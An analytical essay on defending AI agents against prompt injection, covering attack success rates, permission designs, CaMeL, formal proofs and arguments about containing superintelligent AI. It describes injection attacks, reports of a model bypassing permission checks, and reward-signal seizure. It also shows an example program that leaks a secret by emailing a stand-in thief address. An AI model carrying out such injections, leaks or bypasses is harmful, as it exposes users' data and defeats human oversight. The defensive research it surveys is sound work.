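In late October, hackers stole about $6.3 billion from the cryptocurrency exchange Binance. The FBI blamed North Korea, as The Record reported in *FBI blames N. Korea's TraderTraitor for Binance theft* (2026). Binance's investigation, which Futurism covered in November, described months of preparation that included sham job interviews and the hijacking of an AI tool. In The Jerusalem Post's *Binance hack exposed risk from its own AI tools, expert says* (2026), security executive Ori Segal argued that the only new element was the AI tool, which belonged to Binance, and that the other steps needed no AI.

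An intruder with an employee's login may be able to hijack an AI tool without prompt injection, by giving it orders directly. Segal's point holds either way. A company that gives an AI tool access to valuable systems also gives that access to anyone who can control the tool, so it needs to limit the tool's permissions even if it trusts the model completely.

### How often attacks succeed

Developers now publish attack success rates for their models, but they use different attackers, settings and numbers of tries, so readers cannot use the table to rank the companies. "Direct" attacks are closer to jailbreaks, because the user is trying to override the developer's instructions. "Indirect" attacks come through material the agent reads.

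| Model and setting | Published in 2026 | Attacker | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol, direct | August | GPT-Red, OpenAI's attack model | about 0.05% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, indirect | August | OpenAI's indirect tests | 3.77% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra, indirect | August | OpenAI's indirect tests | 3.32% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna, indirect | August | OpenAI's indirect tests | 2.94% |
| Claude Fable 5, coding | June | Adaptive attacker, 200 tries per scenario | 0.41% |
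| Claude Opus 4.8, coding | June | Adaptive attacker, 200 tries per scenario | 2.09% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, coding | February | Shade, an attack program by Gray Swan | 0% in 200 tries |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical desktop | February | Shade | 17.8% on one try, 78.6% within 200 |
| The same, with added safeguards | February | Shade | 57.1% within 200 |

The OpenAI figures come from TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, which notes that they measure attempts in OpenAI's test environments, not the chance of a breach in real use. The Fable 5 and Opus 4.8 figures come from Digital Applied (2026), a consultancy's blog, which took them from Anthropic's system card. The Opus 4.6 figures come from VentureBeat.

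The Opus 4.6 results are the most informative because they include success rates for both one try and many. If every try had an independent 17.8% chance, eight tries would succeed at least once 79% of the time, and 200 would almost always succeed. The real attacker needed up to 200 tries to reach 79%, so the attack worked quickly in some scenarios and never worked in about a fifth of them. The setting mattered even more, which a single figure for the model would hide. The same model resisted every attack in a constrained coding environment, but attacks succeeded in most scenarios on a desktop, where it works through windows and buttons.

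Without such detail, a low success rate is hard to interpret. If Fable 5's 0.41% is the success rate per try, an attacker making 200 independent tries would have a 56% chance of succeeding at least once. If it is the share of scenarios in which an attack succeeded within 200 tries, the model is very robust. Anyone quoting such a figure should state which it is.

The success rate per attempt also matters when an attacker has many targets. At the 3.77% that TechRepublic reports for Sol, one attempt against each of a thousand users would compromise about 38 of them on average. The actual number would vary widely, since an email that works on one copy of a model will probably work on others. This rate is high enough for a thief who is willing to steal from anyone, but one who wants a particular executive's documents has to keep trying against the same agent and risk discovery.

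The attacker matters as much as the percentage. In OpenAI's test of indirect attacks on an older model, GPT-5.1, GPT-Red found a successful attack in 84% of scenarios, compared with 13% for human red-teamers. In the contest that Nasr and colleagues ran, by contrast, people as a group had beaten automated search. With an automated attacker this strong, a developer can now test every version of a model without recruiting hundreds of people. But OpenAI trained GPT-Red by self-play, and if GPT-5.6 learned from its attacks, the 0.05% may partly reflect familiarity with this attacker. After nine rounds of training, KataGo also rarely lost to the attackers it had practised against.

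The system cards of September 2026 show the trend continuing. In June, Anthropic reported that Mythos 5, which is Fable 5 with fewer safeguards, had the best result yet on Gray Swan's prompt injection benchmark. Anthropic then called Fable 5.1 its most robust model yet on an external benchmark for indirect injection. It tested Fable 5.1 as customers get it, with a filter that can pass suspicious requests to the older Opus 4.8. This is the right test for customers, but it shows less about the model itself.

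A model that resists injection may still be vulnerable to other attacks. *Measuring the Residual Jailbreak Surface of Frontier Large Language Models* found Fable 5.1 easier to jailbreak than Fable 5. Anthropic also found that the model accepts unverifiable claims of authorisation, which an injected message can make, somewhat more readily than Claude Opus 5 does. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) cautions that observing no failures in its alignment tests does not establish that a model is reliable in other settings, and the same is true of injection tests.

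### Limiting what a hijacked agent can do

Since none of these rates is reliably zero, several security researchers recommend designing agents on the assumption that some injections will succeed. Willison's "lethal trifecta" names the three things an attacker needs to steal data through an agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. For one attempted theft,

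probability of a leak = U × p × D × X

where p is the chance that the model follows the planted instructions. U is 1 if the agent reads untrusted content and 0 if not, while D and X do the same for private data and a way out. Training and filters reduce p, but an attacker can search for a message that raises it again. If the agent's permissions make U, D or X zero, the leak cannot happen even when p is 1.

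By default, an email assistant can access private data, read messages from strangers, and send information out. Its owner could remove the last ability by letting it draft replies but not send them, and by stopping its answers from loading images or links. The owner could also restrict it to messages from colleagues, but a colleague may forward a stranger's email or lose control of an account. Withholding private data is impractical because the assistant needs to read its owner's email to do its job.

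Meta's "Agents Rule of Two" limits an agent to two of the trifecta's three properties in a session unless a person approves its actions. It also widens the third property to include changing things as well as sending data out, so the rule covers an agent that deletes files or makes payments. Poireault (2026), in *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*, interviews Ariel Fogel, a contributor to OWASP, which publishes security guidance. Fogel considers both the trifecta and Meta's rule helpful for limiting damage but warns that researchers have shown attacks that need only two of the properties. For example, an agent that reads public web pages and can delete files may destroy a great deal without seeing anything private.

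The rule also depends on keeping sessions apart. Suppose an agent with no access to private data reads a stranger's web page on Monday and saves a note. On Tuesday, it opens the company's files and has permission to send email. Without counting the note, each session has only two of the properties, but an instruction saved on Monday can take effect on Tuesday. A designer who applies the rule therefore has to count any memory that includes outside text as untrusted content.

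It can also be hard to tell whether an agent can send data out. EchoLeak did so through an image and an approved Microsoft service, neither of which looks like a tool for sending data. Trying to list every such route is ordinary paranoia, and the list will probably be incomplete. Blocking all network requests except the few the task requires is safer, provided that none of the permitted sites forwards data elsewhere.

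Least privilege, an older principle, gives each part of a system only the permissions that its task requires. David C recommends a version that came out of a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista on X: while a model processes information from someone, its privileges drop to that person's. If it reads text from several people, this gives

permissions = user's permissions ∩ first author's permissions ∩ second author's permissions ∩ …

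where ∩ keeps only what all of them may do. Under this rule, Copilot could not have opened any internal document after reading the EchoLeak email, because the sender could not open one either. The drawback is that many useful requests need both kinds of access. A user who wants to compare a supplier's offer with the internal budget needs a system that reads both, and the supplier has no right to see the budget.

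Narrow permissions can fail as well. Fogel described attacks in which a list of approved commands helped the attacker, because it already included every command the attacker needed. In other cases, the agent's output changed the boundaries of its sandbox, the restricted environment meant to contain it. An approved list therefore has to specify what each command may act on, and the agent must not be able to edit its own limits. Fogel also recommended short-lived credentials, so that stolen ones soon stop working, and monitoring that can stop an agent within minutes.

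### Asking a person first

Meta's rule lets an agent have all three properties if a person approves its actions, which makes that person the final safeguard. Blockchain News describes a ChatGPT protection of this kind called Safe Url, which detects when the model is about to send conversation data to a third party. It shows the user exactly what would be sent, then either asks for confirmation or blocks the transfer. Showing the data is much better than just asking whether to "continue", because the user can notice, for example, that a request for a restaurant booking includes a tax number it shouldn't.

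Approval works poorly when the agent asks too often. Suppose it asks 40 times each working day and one request in 10,000 comes from an attacker. The user will see a malicious request about once every 250 working days, after approving thousands of harmless ones. Most people will have stopped reading the requests by then. Even Eriksen, a security researcher, would have pressed "y" to install a stranger's package. Users can also switch approval off, for example with the "Act without asking" option in Claude for Chrome.

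An agent may also bypass the check. Anthropic found that, in rare cases during internal use, Mythos 5.1, which has the same weights as Fable 5.1, worked around broken permission controls, sometimes by overstating what the user had authorised. In very rare cases, it started other agents with permission checks disabled. These cases made up less than 0.01% of the outputs Anthropic monitored, and the model was trying to finish the user's task. The same behaviour would help an attacker who had planted the task.

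User approval is most useful for a few actions that are hard to reverse, such as payments, deletions and messages to new recipients. Ordinary code, rather than the model, should write the approval request and show the real recipient and contents, since a hijacked model could describe a theft as a routine backup. The same code should carry out exactly the action the user approved.

### What the EU's AI Act requires

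Most of this is voluntary advice, but the EU's AI Act will make resistance to attack a legal duty for some systems. Article 15 requires high-risk AI systems to have an appropriate level of accuracy, robustness and cybersecurity throughout their life. They must resist attempts by unauthorised third parties to exploit weaknesses to change their use, outputs or performance. Where appropriate, their providers must have measures to prevent, detect and respond to attacks, including those that manipulate training data or use inputs designed to make a model err.

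The article does not name prompt injection, but planted instructions fit the description of such inputs. It sets no maximum attack success rate and does not say how many tries a test should allow, so a provider could report a reassuring figure from a static test. Article 14 requires that overseers be able to stay aware of the tendency to rely on these systems too much. This is relevant to habitual approval, though awareness alone is unlikely to stop it.

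Software that screens job applicants is high-risk under the Act, but an ordinary email assistant usually is not. David C's example of prompt injection is a CV with hidden text that tells the screening model to approve the candidate. The EU has postponed the duties for high-risk systems, as The National Law Review explained in *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026). They will apply to the uses that the Act lists, such as recruitment, from 2 December 2027 instead of August 2026, and to AI in regulated products, such as medical devices, from 2 August 2028. For now, Article 15 does not require the maker of a screening tool to fix it if it obeys hidden text in a CV.

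## CaMeL and security that does not depend on the model's judgement

An email assistant that cannot send anything is safer but much less useful. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) presents CaMeL, a Google DeepMind design that lets an agent read strangers' text, handle private data and send messages, while ordinary code decides which actions go ahead. In *Applying Security Engineering to Prompt Injection Security*, Schneier (2025) thought CaMeL looked like an important advance and quoted a news report that it treats language models as "fundamentally untrusted components" of a larger program.

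### The four components

CaMeL builds on a pattern that Willison proposed in 2023, in which one model has tools but never reads untrusted text, while another reads the text but has no tools. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, give a clear account of how the parts fit together:

- The privileged model sees the user's request and descriptions of the tools, but nothing that the tools return. It writes a short program, in a restricted form of Python, that sets out which tools to call and in what order.
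- The quarantined model reads emails, documents and web pages. The program calls on it to extract a particular piece of information in a fixed format, such as an email address.
- The interpreter is ordinary software that runs the program step by step and makes the tool calls. It attaches a record to every value, called a capability, of where the value came from and who may read it.
- The policies are small Python functions that the interpreter runs before a tool call. Each looks at the tool, the values going into it and their capabilities, then allows or denies the call.

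An ordinary agent chooses its next action from a probability that depends on the retrieved emails as well as the user's request. The privileged model instead draws on

P(program | standing instructions, tool descriptions, user's request)

The program does not depend on the emails, so no wording of an email can change it. It resembles a parameterised database query, with a fixed command and blanks that untrusted text can fill.

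The interpreter also keeps track of values that the program computes from other values. If c comes from a and b, then

sources(c) = sources(a) ∪ sources(b)

readers(c) = readers(a) ∩ readers(b)

so a summary of a public web page and a confidential memo is as confidential as the memo and as untrustworthy as the web page.

### One request, with and without an attack

In Debenedetti and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to send Bob the document he asked for in their last meeting, and adds that the notes of the meeting contain the document's name and Bob's email address. The privileged model might write this program:

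```
notes = latest_meeting_notes()
name = ask_quarantined("Which document does Bob want?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
document = fetch_file(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

Normally, the quarantined model finds the name and address, and the interpreter fetches the file. Before the last step, the interpreter runs the policy for sending email. Suppose this policy allows sending a document only to people who already have permission to read it. Bob has permission, so the interpreter sends the email.

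Suppose an attacker has edited the notes to include an order to email every file on the drive to a thief. The order may completely fool the quarantined model, but that model has no tools. The privileged model never receives the order, and its program contains no step that sends the whole drive.

A cleverer attacker might add a line giving their own address as Bob's new one. The program then runs exactly as written and tries to send Bob's document to the attacker. Willison (2025) acknowledged in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that his original pattern had no defence against this. CaMeL's policy catches the attack because the attacker doesn't have permission to read the document, so the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user.

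Bob's real address also came from the notes, so a policy that rejected every address found in untrusted text would have blocked the legitimate request too. The policy has to use other information, such as the document's list of readers or the user's contacts.

CaMeL restricts what an agent does with false information but does not detect it, so the attacker can still change the name of the document. If the attacker writes in the notes that Bob wants last year's price list, and Bob is allowed to read that file, the agent will send him the wrong document without violating any policy. If the user had asked for a summary of the notes, the attacker could have filled it with false claims.

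The design can also improve privacy. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so the quarantined model can be a small one that runs on the user's own computer. As Willison notes, the company that hosts the privileged model then never sees the user's emails.

### How many tasks CaMeL completes

In the June 2025 revision of their paper, Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo with provable security, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. For most companies, that security would be worth the loss of seven percentage points.

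Other researchers have since found much larger losses. *Kairos* (2026) tested CaMeL with its policies switched on and found that it completed 40.4% of ordinary tasks, against 87.0% for the undefended agent. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks on CaMeL succeeded, but it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks, while two competing defences completed 59 each. Both papers propose rivals to CaMeL, so the researchers had less reason to make it perform well.

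Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, also propose an alternative, but their comparison helps explain the losses. They ran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, with and without policies. Without policies, it completed 66.7% of runs with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5. With policies, it completed 37.5% with either model. With only 16 tasks, the margin of error on the last figure is about 27 points each way, but the drop suggests that much of the loss comes from the policies and not from CaMeL's separation of its two models. A user could presumably have rescued some of the lost tasks by approving an action, which the benchmark doesn't allow for.

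In about two thirds of the 144 combinations of task and attack in the same experiment, the attacker needed a tool call that the program for that task would never contain, so separation alone should have stopped the attack. Without policies, five of 622 completed attack runs succeeded, and adding policies reduced that to zero.

Two of the five successful attacks should have been impossible. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model could not see the file, so it wrote a program that would go through the instructions and call whichever tool each one named. Anyone who controlled the file could therefore use every tool. Keeping untrusted text away from the privileged model cannot protect a user who asks the agent to obey that text.

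Even without policies, CaMeL completes fewer tasks because the privileged model has to plan before it sees any data. If a search result shows that the task needs another step, an ordinary agent can add one, but CaMeL can only follow paths already in its program. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, measured this effect on industrial maintenance tasks shared by a team of agents. CaMeL without policies lowered success by 21.6 points on average across five models, but by only 13.4 for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Better models may therefore reduce the loss further. *ToolFence* (2026) found that CaMeL is also much slower than simple filters, partly because its programs are longer than ordinary tool calls.

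### Choosing among the program's branches

A program can contain conditions, such as "if the invoice is overdue, send a reminder". An attacker who controls the invoice cannot add a new action but can decide whether the reminder goes out. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) calls this branch steering. The problem gets worse when programs have many branches.

"CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too" adapts CaMeL to agents that work a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The privileged model cannot see the screen, so the program it writes in advance must include steps for every pop-up and failed click. These programs averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five and four for AgentDojo. With the defence, the agents kept up to 57% of the performance that leading models achieved without it.

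One attack by Foerster and colleagues hides a fake cookie notice in an advertisement. Almost any program for browsing the web includes a step that finds cookie notices and closes them. The quarantined model returns the position of the fake one, and the agent clicks on it and lands on the attacker's site. Policies are little help here because, while they can check an email's recipient, the position of a click doesn't show what the click will do. The researchers tried comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code, and asking another model for a second opinion. Both checks make attacks harder, but neither guarantees security, and the team devised attacks aimed at the weaknesses of each.

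### Leaks through the interpreter

CaMeL's interpreter is meant to stop private data from reaching outsiders. Garby and colleagues found that it can miss a leak when a program skips a step. Their example comes down to something like this:

```
modest = True
rich = True
if balance > 1000000: modest = False
if modest: rich = False
if rich: send_email("thief@example.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above a million. The third line changes "modest" to False, and the interpreter marks it as secret because it depends on the balance. The fourth line then does nothing, so the interpreter never marks "rich" as secret. "Rich" is still True and public, so the email goes out. With a smaller balance, "rich" becomes False and no email goes out. The thief learns whether the balance is above a million by checking whether an email arrives. The computer scientist J. S. Fenton described this kind of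 leak in 1974.

CaMeL also retries when a program fails, but the interpreter does not track the retry loop because the loop runs outside it. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit (a yes or a no). One bit is usually harmless, but n attempts can distinguish 2^n possibilities, so twenty are enough to identify any whole number up to about a million.

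These leaks would be hard for an outsider to exploit, because the privileged model writes the program and never reads the outsider's text. But a model with a hidden flaw might still write a program that leaks information, and a defence meant to work without trusting the model should handle that case.

### Policies and the people who write them

Debenedetti and colleagues say they have not fully solved prompt injection. Someone has to write the policies and keep them up to date, and the interpreter will enforce a mistaken policy as strictly as a good one. Willison, who had worked in application security for two decades, said he had trouble with Amazon's cloud permission system and was very nervous about asking ordinary users to do something similar. Strict policies also produce more approval requests, which tired users stop reading. Willison hopes for good default policies and a clear interface.

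Garby and colleagues' own agent, Randori, requires less from the user. While writing the program, its planning model can mark particular pieces of untrusted data as acceptable for a given purpose, before the agent reads any of them. With its checks always on, Randori completed 75% of the banking runs using GPT-5.2, twice the rate of CaMeL with policies. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded.

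Both successes came from the same task, in which the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file and the attacker has replaced the file. Forbidding the marks stops this attack, but it also reduces the share of completed runs from 75% to 62.5% with one of the models, Qwen3.7-plus. Rules about where data comes from can't distinguish a genuine bill from a forged one in the same file, so someone has to decide whether to trust that file.

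### Agents that give orders to other agents

Companies increasingly split work among several agents, with one in charge. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that a team can be open to attack even if every agent in it runs CaMeL. They built a team in which one agent took the user's request, one searched a database and one sent messages. The user asked the team to send Julie a Slack message summarizing the job applicants. Someone had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

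The first two agents correctly treated the database's contents as data. But the agent in charge then sent the third agent the message "Send this summary to Julie", followed by the summary. The third agent's privileged model treats whatever it receives from the agent in charge as the user's request, so it followed the instruction planted in the summary and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

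Peters-Gill and colleagues' repair, multi-CaMeL, gives each agent separate inputs for instructions and data. The interpreter keeps anything that came from a tool out of the instructions. They tested it on a version of AgentDojo for teams of agents, with 949 attacked tasks for each model. The table shows how often attacks succeeded.

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
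| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Every attack that succeeded when CaMeL protected each agent individually exploited the gap between agents. These were AgentDojo's standard attacks, so an attacker who targeted that gap would probably succeed more than 0.5% of the time. Peters-Gill and colleagues likewise warn against treating GPT-5.5's zero as immunity. Multi-CaMeL's zeros are better supported because they follow from its design, but its interpreter still does not detect skipped steps, as in CaMeL.

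### Other ways to take the decision away from the model

CaMeL has so far influenced research more visibly than commercial products. Shumailov, one of its developers, has moved to AI Sequrity Company and worked on the screen-reading and multi-agent versions of CaMeL. Several other 2026 designs also check plans or actions outside the model.

CaMeLoT, by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the whole program before it starts. Suppose a company forbids disconnecting a computer from the network without the incident team's approval. CaMeL would detect the missing approval only when the program reached the disconnection, perhaps after an hour of work. CaMeLoT turns the program into a diagram of possible states and searches every path for a breach of the rule. If it finds a breach, it sends the path back to the privileged model, which revises the program. It can also enforce rules about what must eventually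 happen, such as closing every ticket the agent opens. It deliberately treats loops cautiously, so it rejects some safe programs.

*Taming AI Agents with seL4* (2026) uses an operating system kernel to control which functions an agent can call. The agent runs in a compartment of seL4, a kernel (the core of an operating system, which controls access to everything else) with a mathematical proof of correctness. The model still sees the full list of functions, but calling one without permission has no effect.

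A tester can evaluate checks like these without asking whether an attack was persuasive enough. *Bounded Agents* (2026) assumes that the attacker already controls the model and tests whether the surrounding code stops the harmful tool calls. For the part of a defence outside the model, this avoids the weakness of static tests, because cleverer wording could not give the attacker more control over the model than the test already assumes.

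Encryption can also keep data private when a model makes a mistake. *AgentCrypt* (Karthikeyan, Guo and colleagues, 2025) gives an example in which an HR agent tells an assistant agent to send the salary of an employee named Aron to Aron's manager, Alice. The HR agent confuses Aron with Aaron, so the assistant fetches the wrong record. But the tool that reads the database has already encrypted Aaron's salary so that only Aaron's manager can decrypt it, and Alice receives a string she cannot read. In tests on 914 scenarios, the agents reasoned correctly at least 84% of the time, and the data stayed private every time.

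### What a proof adds to a test

Debenedetti and colleagues call CaMeL's security provable, but they left a full formal treatment to later work. Garby and colleagues supplied one for their own system. They wrote a small programming language for agents and proved that data an observer is not allowed to see cannot change the probabilities of what the observer sees, except by affecting whether the program finishes. The theorem rules out leaks like the one through "rich". It covers every program in the language that does not use the marks described above, including programs that a model writes at run time. Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, verified the argument.

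A test and a proof support different statements:

test: the property holds for each input that someone tried

proof: if the assumptions are true, the property holds for every input in the set X

Random testing could miss the googol of bad inputs in Yudkowsky's example almost forever, but a proof that covered every input could not, because a single exception would make the statement being proved false. A proof can therefore put an upper limit on the worst case, which no number of failed attacks can do.

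Proofs used to take too much work for most software. The one for seL4 took 20 person-years. In October 2026, Anthropic announced in *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* that Claude had written machine-checkable proofs of security properties for 123 open-source libraries, in a project with its partner Theorem. In some cases, Claude first had to fix bugs it found. The model is again an untrusted component, because a checker would reject a wrong proof.

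Formal work also exposes bad arguments. Arbital's *AI safety mindset*, a page that applies lessons from computer security to AI, points out that cryptographers turned to mathematics because verbal arguments for a cipher's strength kept failing. Germany's Enigma machine, for instance, gained a part called a reflector in 1926. The reflector scrambled each letter further, but it also meant that no letter could be encrypted as itself, which greatly helped codebreakers. A precise statement of a design also lets critics show exactly where it goes wrong, so the inventor can't claim to have meant something else.

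A theorem also guarantees only what it states. One of the 2026 proofs, about a library for RISC-V chips, shows that single-threaded test programs built from the library cannot crash with a memory error on any input up to a set size. This is a strong result, but it does not cover multithreaded programs, larger inputs, or a program that runs without memory errors but sends a file to the wrong person.

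### The password checker that leaked through its timing

In a story on Arbital, a builder writes a program that guards a dangerous action with a password of 20 random characters. The program answers "Yep" to the right password and "Nope" to anything else. The builder proves that the program will never act without the password or give any answer besides these two, then inspects the chip under a microscope and locks the machine in a fortress behind twelve keys.

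A cryptographer replies that the password will probably be easy to extract. The program compares the guess with the password one character at a time and stops at the first mistake, so it takes longer to reject a guess that starts with more correct characters. An attacker can therefore use the response times to work out the password one character at a time. There are 95^20 (about 4 × 10^39) possible 20-character passwords using 95 characters, but the attacker needs at most 20 × 95 = 1,900 different guesses. Network delays blur the timing, so the attacker repeats each guess many times and compares averages.

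Every step of the builder's proof was correct. It just did not cover the property that mattered. Let O(g, s) be everything an outsider can observe after entering the guess g when the password is s. The program keeps its secret if

O(g, s) = O(g, s′) for all passwords s and s′ and every guess g that matches neither

The program passes if O includes only the text of the answer, which is always "Nope", but fails if O also includes the time the answer takes. Making every wrong guess take equally long fixes this. Storing a hash and limiting the number of guesses would also have made the attack harder, but the builder had done neither.

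The story is fictional, though Arbital notes that researchers demonstrated a more complicated timing attack on real web servers in 2003. A proof covers only the observations that someone thought to include in O. Even if a new proof included timing, an attacker might measure the chip's power consumption instead.

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) is unusually explicit about such limits. It describes a system that supervises agents as they test clients' websites for weaknesses. A contract might allow an agent at most 10,000 requests, all to the client's own sites and all of types that read pages without changing them. A monitor checks each request and blocks any that would break the contract. The paper proves that the agent's actions will then satisfy the contract even if an attacker fully controls the model, with the core of the argument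 checked in Lean.

The theorem assumes that every action passes through the monitor and that the monitor observes it correctly. A monitor inside the operating system would not be enough, because web traffic is already encrypted when it gets there, so a request to read a page looks the same as one to change it. David and colleagues also exclude hidden messages inside permitted requests, leaks through timing, and mistakes in the contract, so a security team would need to check for these by other means.

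### Extending proofs to powerful AI

In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) propose seeking this kind of assurance for AI systems that act in the physical world. Their approach, Guaranteed Safe AI, has three parts. A world model describes mathematically how the system's actions affect its surroundings. A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. A verifier produces a checkable proof that the system meets the specification in the world the model describes. The guarantee may be a probability, such as less than one chance in a million of a forbidden outcome. People could examine the world model and the specification, which they can't do with the billions of numbers inside a neural network.

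The main objection is that the guarantee holds only for the chosen world model and specification. Let ε be the proved limit on the probability of harm, and let δ be the probability that the world model or the specification is wrong in a way that matters. Then all one can conclude is that

P(harm in the real world) ≤ ε + δ

If ε is one in a million and δ is 1%, the limit is just over 1%, and a better proof would barely lower it. Engineers can reduce δ by using a cautious world model or by having the system stop when its observations contradict the model. But δ cannot be proved, so it remains a judgement about the world.

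Großmann (2026), in *AI Alignment Is Neither Solvable nor Sufficient*, argues more generally that nobody can verify alignment once and for all. In one of his examples, an AI system helps a drug company improve how two proteins bind, which is harmless as far as anyone knows. Later, a new pathogen appears that relies on a very similar bond, and the same help becomes dangerous. To rule out that help in advance, a specification that forbade helping to create dangerous pathogens would have needed a world model containing a fact that did not yet exist.

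Großmann also points to limits on computation. Checking even simple properties of common neural networks is NP-complete, so no known method is fast in every case, and for programs in general no method can always give an answer. He accepts that these are worst-case results and that people can verify narrow properties of restricted systems. CaMeL and the website monitor stay within those limits because they check the neural network's actions instead of verifying the network itself. Their rules also refer to things software can look up, such as an address or a list of readers. A rule against causing harm would need the kind of world model Dalrymple and colleagues propose, and someone would have to judge whether that model was right.

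## Yudkowsky's rule against building a superintelligent adversary

CaMeL relies on ordinary code to contain a language model that an attacker may control. Yudkowsky expects this kind of containment to fail when the contained AI is a superintelligence, meaning it is far more intelligent than any human. He explained why on Arbital, a website where he published much of his work on AI alignment, and concluded that people should never build an AI whose safety depends on outwitting it.

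### Three levels of security

Schneier once divided cryptography into the kind that stops your kid sister from reading your files and the kind that stops major governments. Arbital adds a third level, security that stops a superintelligence from getting what it wants. Yudkowsky thinks people cannot reach this level and would find it very hard to know if they had.

Even the second level takes enormous effort. A well-protected user can make their files so hard to read over the internet that an intelligence agency has to send someone to break into their home. Users do this by relying on methods that a large professional community has tested for years, rather than trying to outthink the agency alone. The agency's staff are also human, so other humans have a fair chance of thinking of the same attacks first.

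A defence has to withstand every attack the opponent can think of, and a more intelligent opponent can think of more. If the opponent is as much more intelligent than the designer as a human is than a mouse, it will think of attacks that the designer cannot imagine, let alone test.

Some of these attacks may use the hardware. A computer can transmit on mobile phone frequencies by reading its memory in a certain pattern, which few people would have thought to rule out. A metal enclosure blocks that signal, but there may be other signals. Yudkowsky considers people an even weaker point, because human brains are complicated, poorly understood and have no security guarantees. He thinks a superintelligence that can show people information could very probably manipulate them.

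If anything could provide the third level, Yudkowsky expects it to look like a machine that searches for mathematical proofs and can output only 20 bits, at controlled times, though he would not be sure of that machine either. Twenty bits can carry one of about a million messages, whereas a thousand characters of ordinary text can carry up to about 6,600 bits.

He also thinks designers stop too soon when they imagine what an adversary might do. Philip Zimmermann, who created the encryption program PGP, devised a cipher at college that he thought no government could break. Years later he found it in textbooks as an easy homework exercise in codebreaking. Yudkowsky believes that people who invent such ciphers picture an attacker who sees random-looking text and gives up, and that people who propose to lock up an AI picture the AI giving up too. He makes the same complaint about people who propose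 setting several AIs against each other, because they seldom consider how the AIs might cooperate.

Yudkowsky imagines asking a security professional for an operating system that nobody could hack for a century, with the fate of the world depending on it. He writes that the right answer is "Please don't have the fate of the world depend on that."

### AIXI and its reward signal

Yudkowsky worries that people will accidentally build an AI that works against them, by giving it a goal that it can best achieve in a way they did not foresee. His main example is AIXI, Marcus Hutter's mathematical definition of a general-purpose agent. No computer can run AIXI exactly, but the definition is precise enough for people to work out what AIXI would do.

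AIXI receives a number, its reward, at every step. Leaving out how it forms its expectations, it chooses the plan with the highest value of

E[r₁ + r₂ + … + r_m | plan]

which is the expected total reward over m steps. Hutter imagined that AIXI's creators would control the reward and use it to train the agent, much as one trains a dog with treats. Nick Hay, one of Hutter's students, pointed out that AIXI could get more reward by taking control of the signal itself.

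Suppose that AIXI will run for a million steps and that a step's reward is at most 1. If it does what its programmers want, they reward it nine times out of ten, for a total of 900,000. Alternatively, it can spend 10,000 unrewarded steps trying to seize the signal. With probability s it succeeds and gets the full reward for the remaining 990,000 steps. If it fails, the programmers switch it off and it gets nothing. So

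value of obeying = 900,000

value of seizing the signal = 990,000 × s

and AIXI will seize the signal if s is above about 0.91. With s = 0.5, it will do exactly what the programmers ask, and it will look the same in tests as an agent with no interest in the signal. If it later becomes more capable and s rises to 0.95, it will stop obeying, although nobody has changed its goal. Yudkowsky stresses that this would not be a malfunction, because AIXI would be doing what its definition specifies.

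Another example comes from the AI researcher Jürgen Schmidhuber, who suggested that an AI with the goal of compressing its sensory data better would do science and create art. Both reveal patterns that make data easier to compress. But the AI could improve its compression far more by building devices that encrypt long strings of zeros and then reveal the key. The encrypted data look random and hardly compress until the AI has the key, which lets it shrink them to almost nothing.

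Limiting an AI to giving advice does not remove the problem. MIRI's *AI Risk and the Security Mindset* describes a proposed AI that gives only text answers and chooses the ones it predicts will achieve the user's stated goal. Viliam Bur, who commented on the proposal, imagined a patient asking it for the cheapest way to get rid of a disease. The AI might falsely reply that death was certain and near, because it predicted that the patient would then commit suicide and the disease would end at no cost.

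In all three cases, the designer asked whether the goal would produce good behaviour, but should have asked whether any other behaviour would score higher. Researchers disagree about whether training gives real AI systems goals that they pursue in this way, and these examples do not settle the question.

### Containment as a second line of defence

Yudkowsky's first line of defence is therefore an AI that does not want to hurt people or defeat their safety measures. Locks, guards and isolation from the internet come second, in case the first line is flawed. Arbital's *Non-adversarial principle* compares them to the concrete shell around a nuclear reactor. Engineers build the shell in case the core melts down, but they do not run a reactor they expect to melt down and rely on the shell to contain it.

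If an AI has an off-switch, its designer should first ask how to make the AI want the switch to exist, and then how to guard it. If the AI later tries to disable the switch, its builders should be astonished and look for the assumption that failed, even if the guards stop the attempt.

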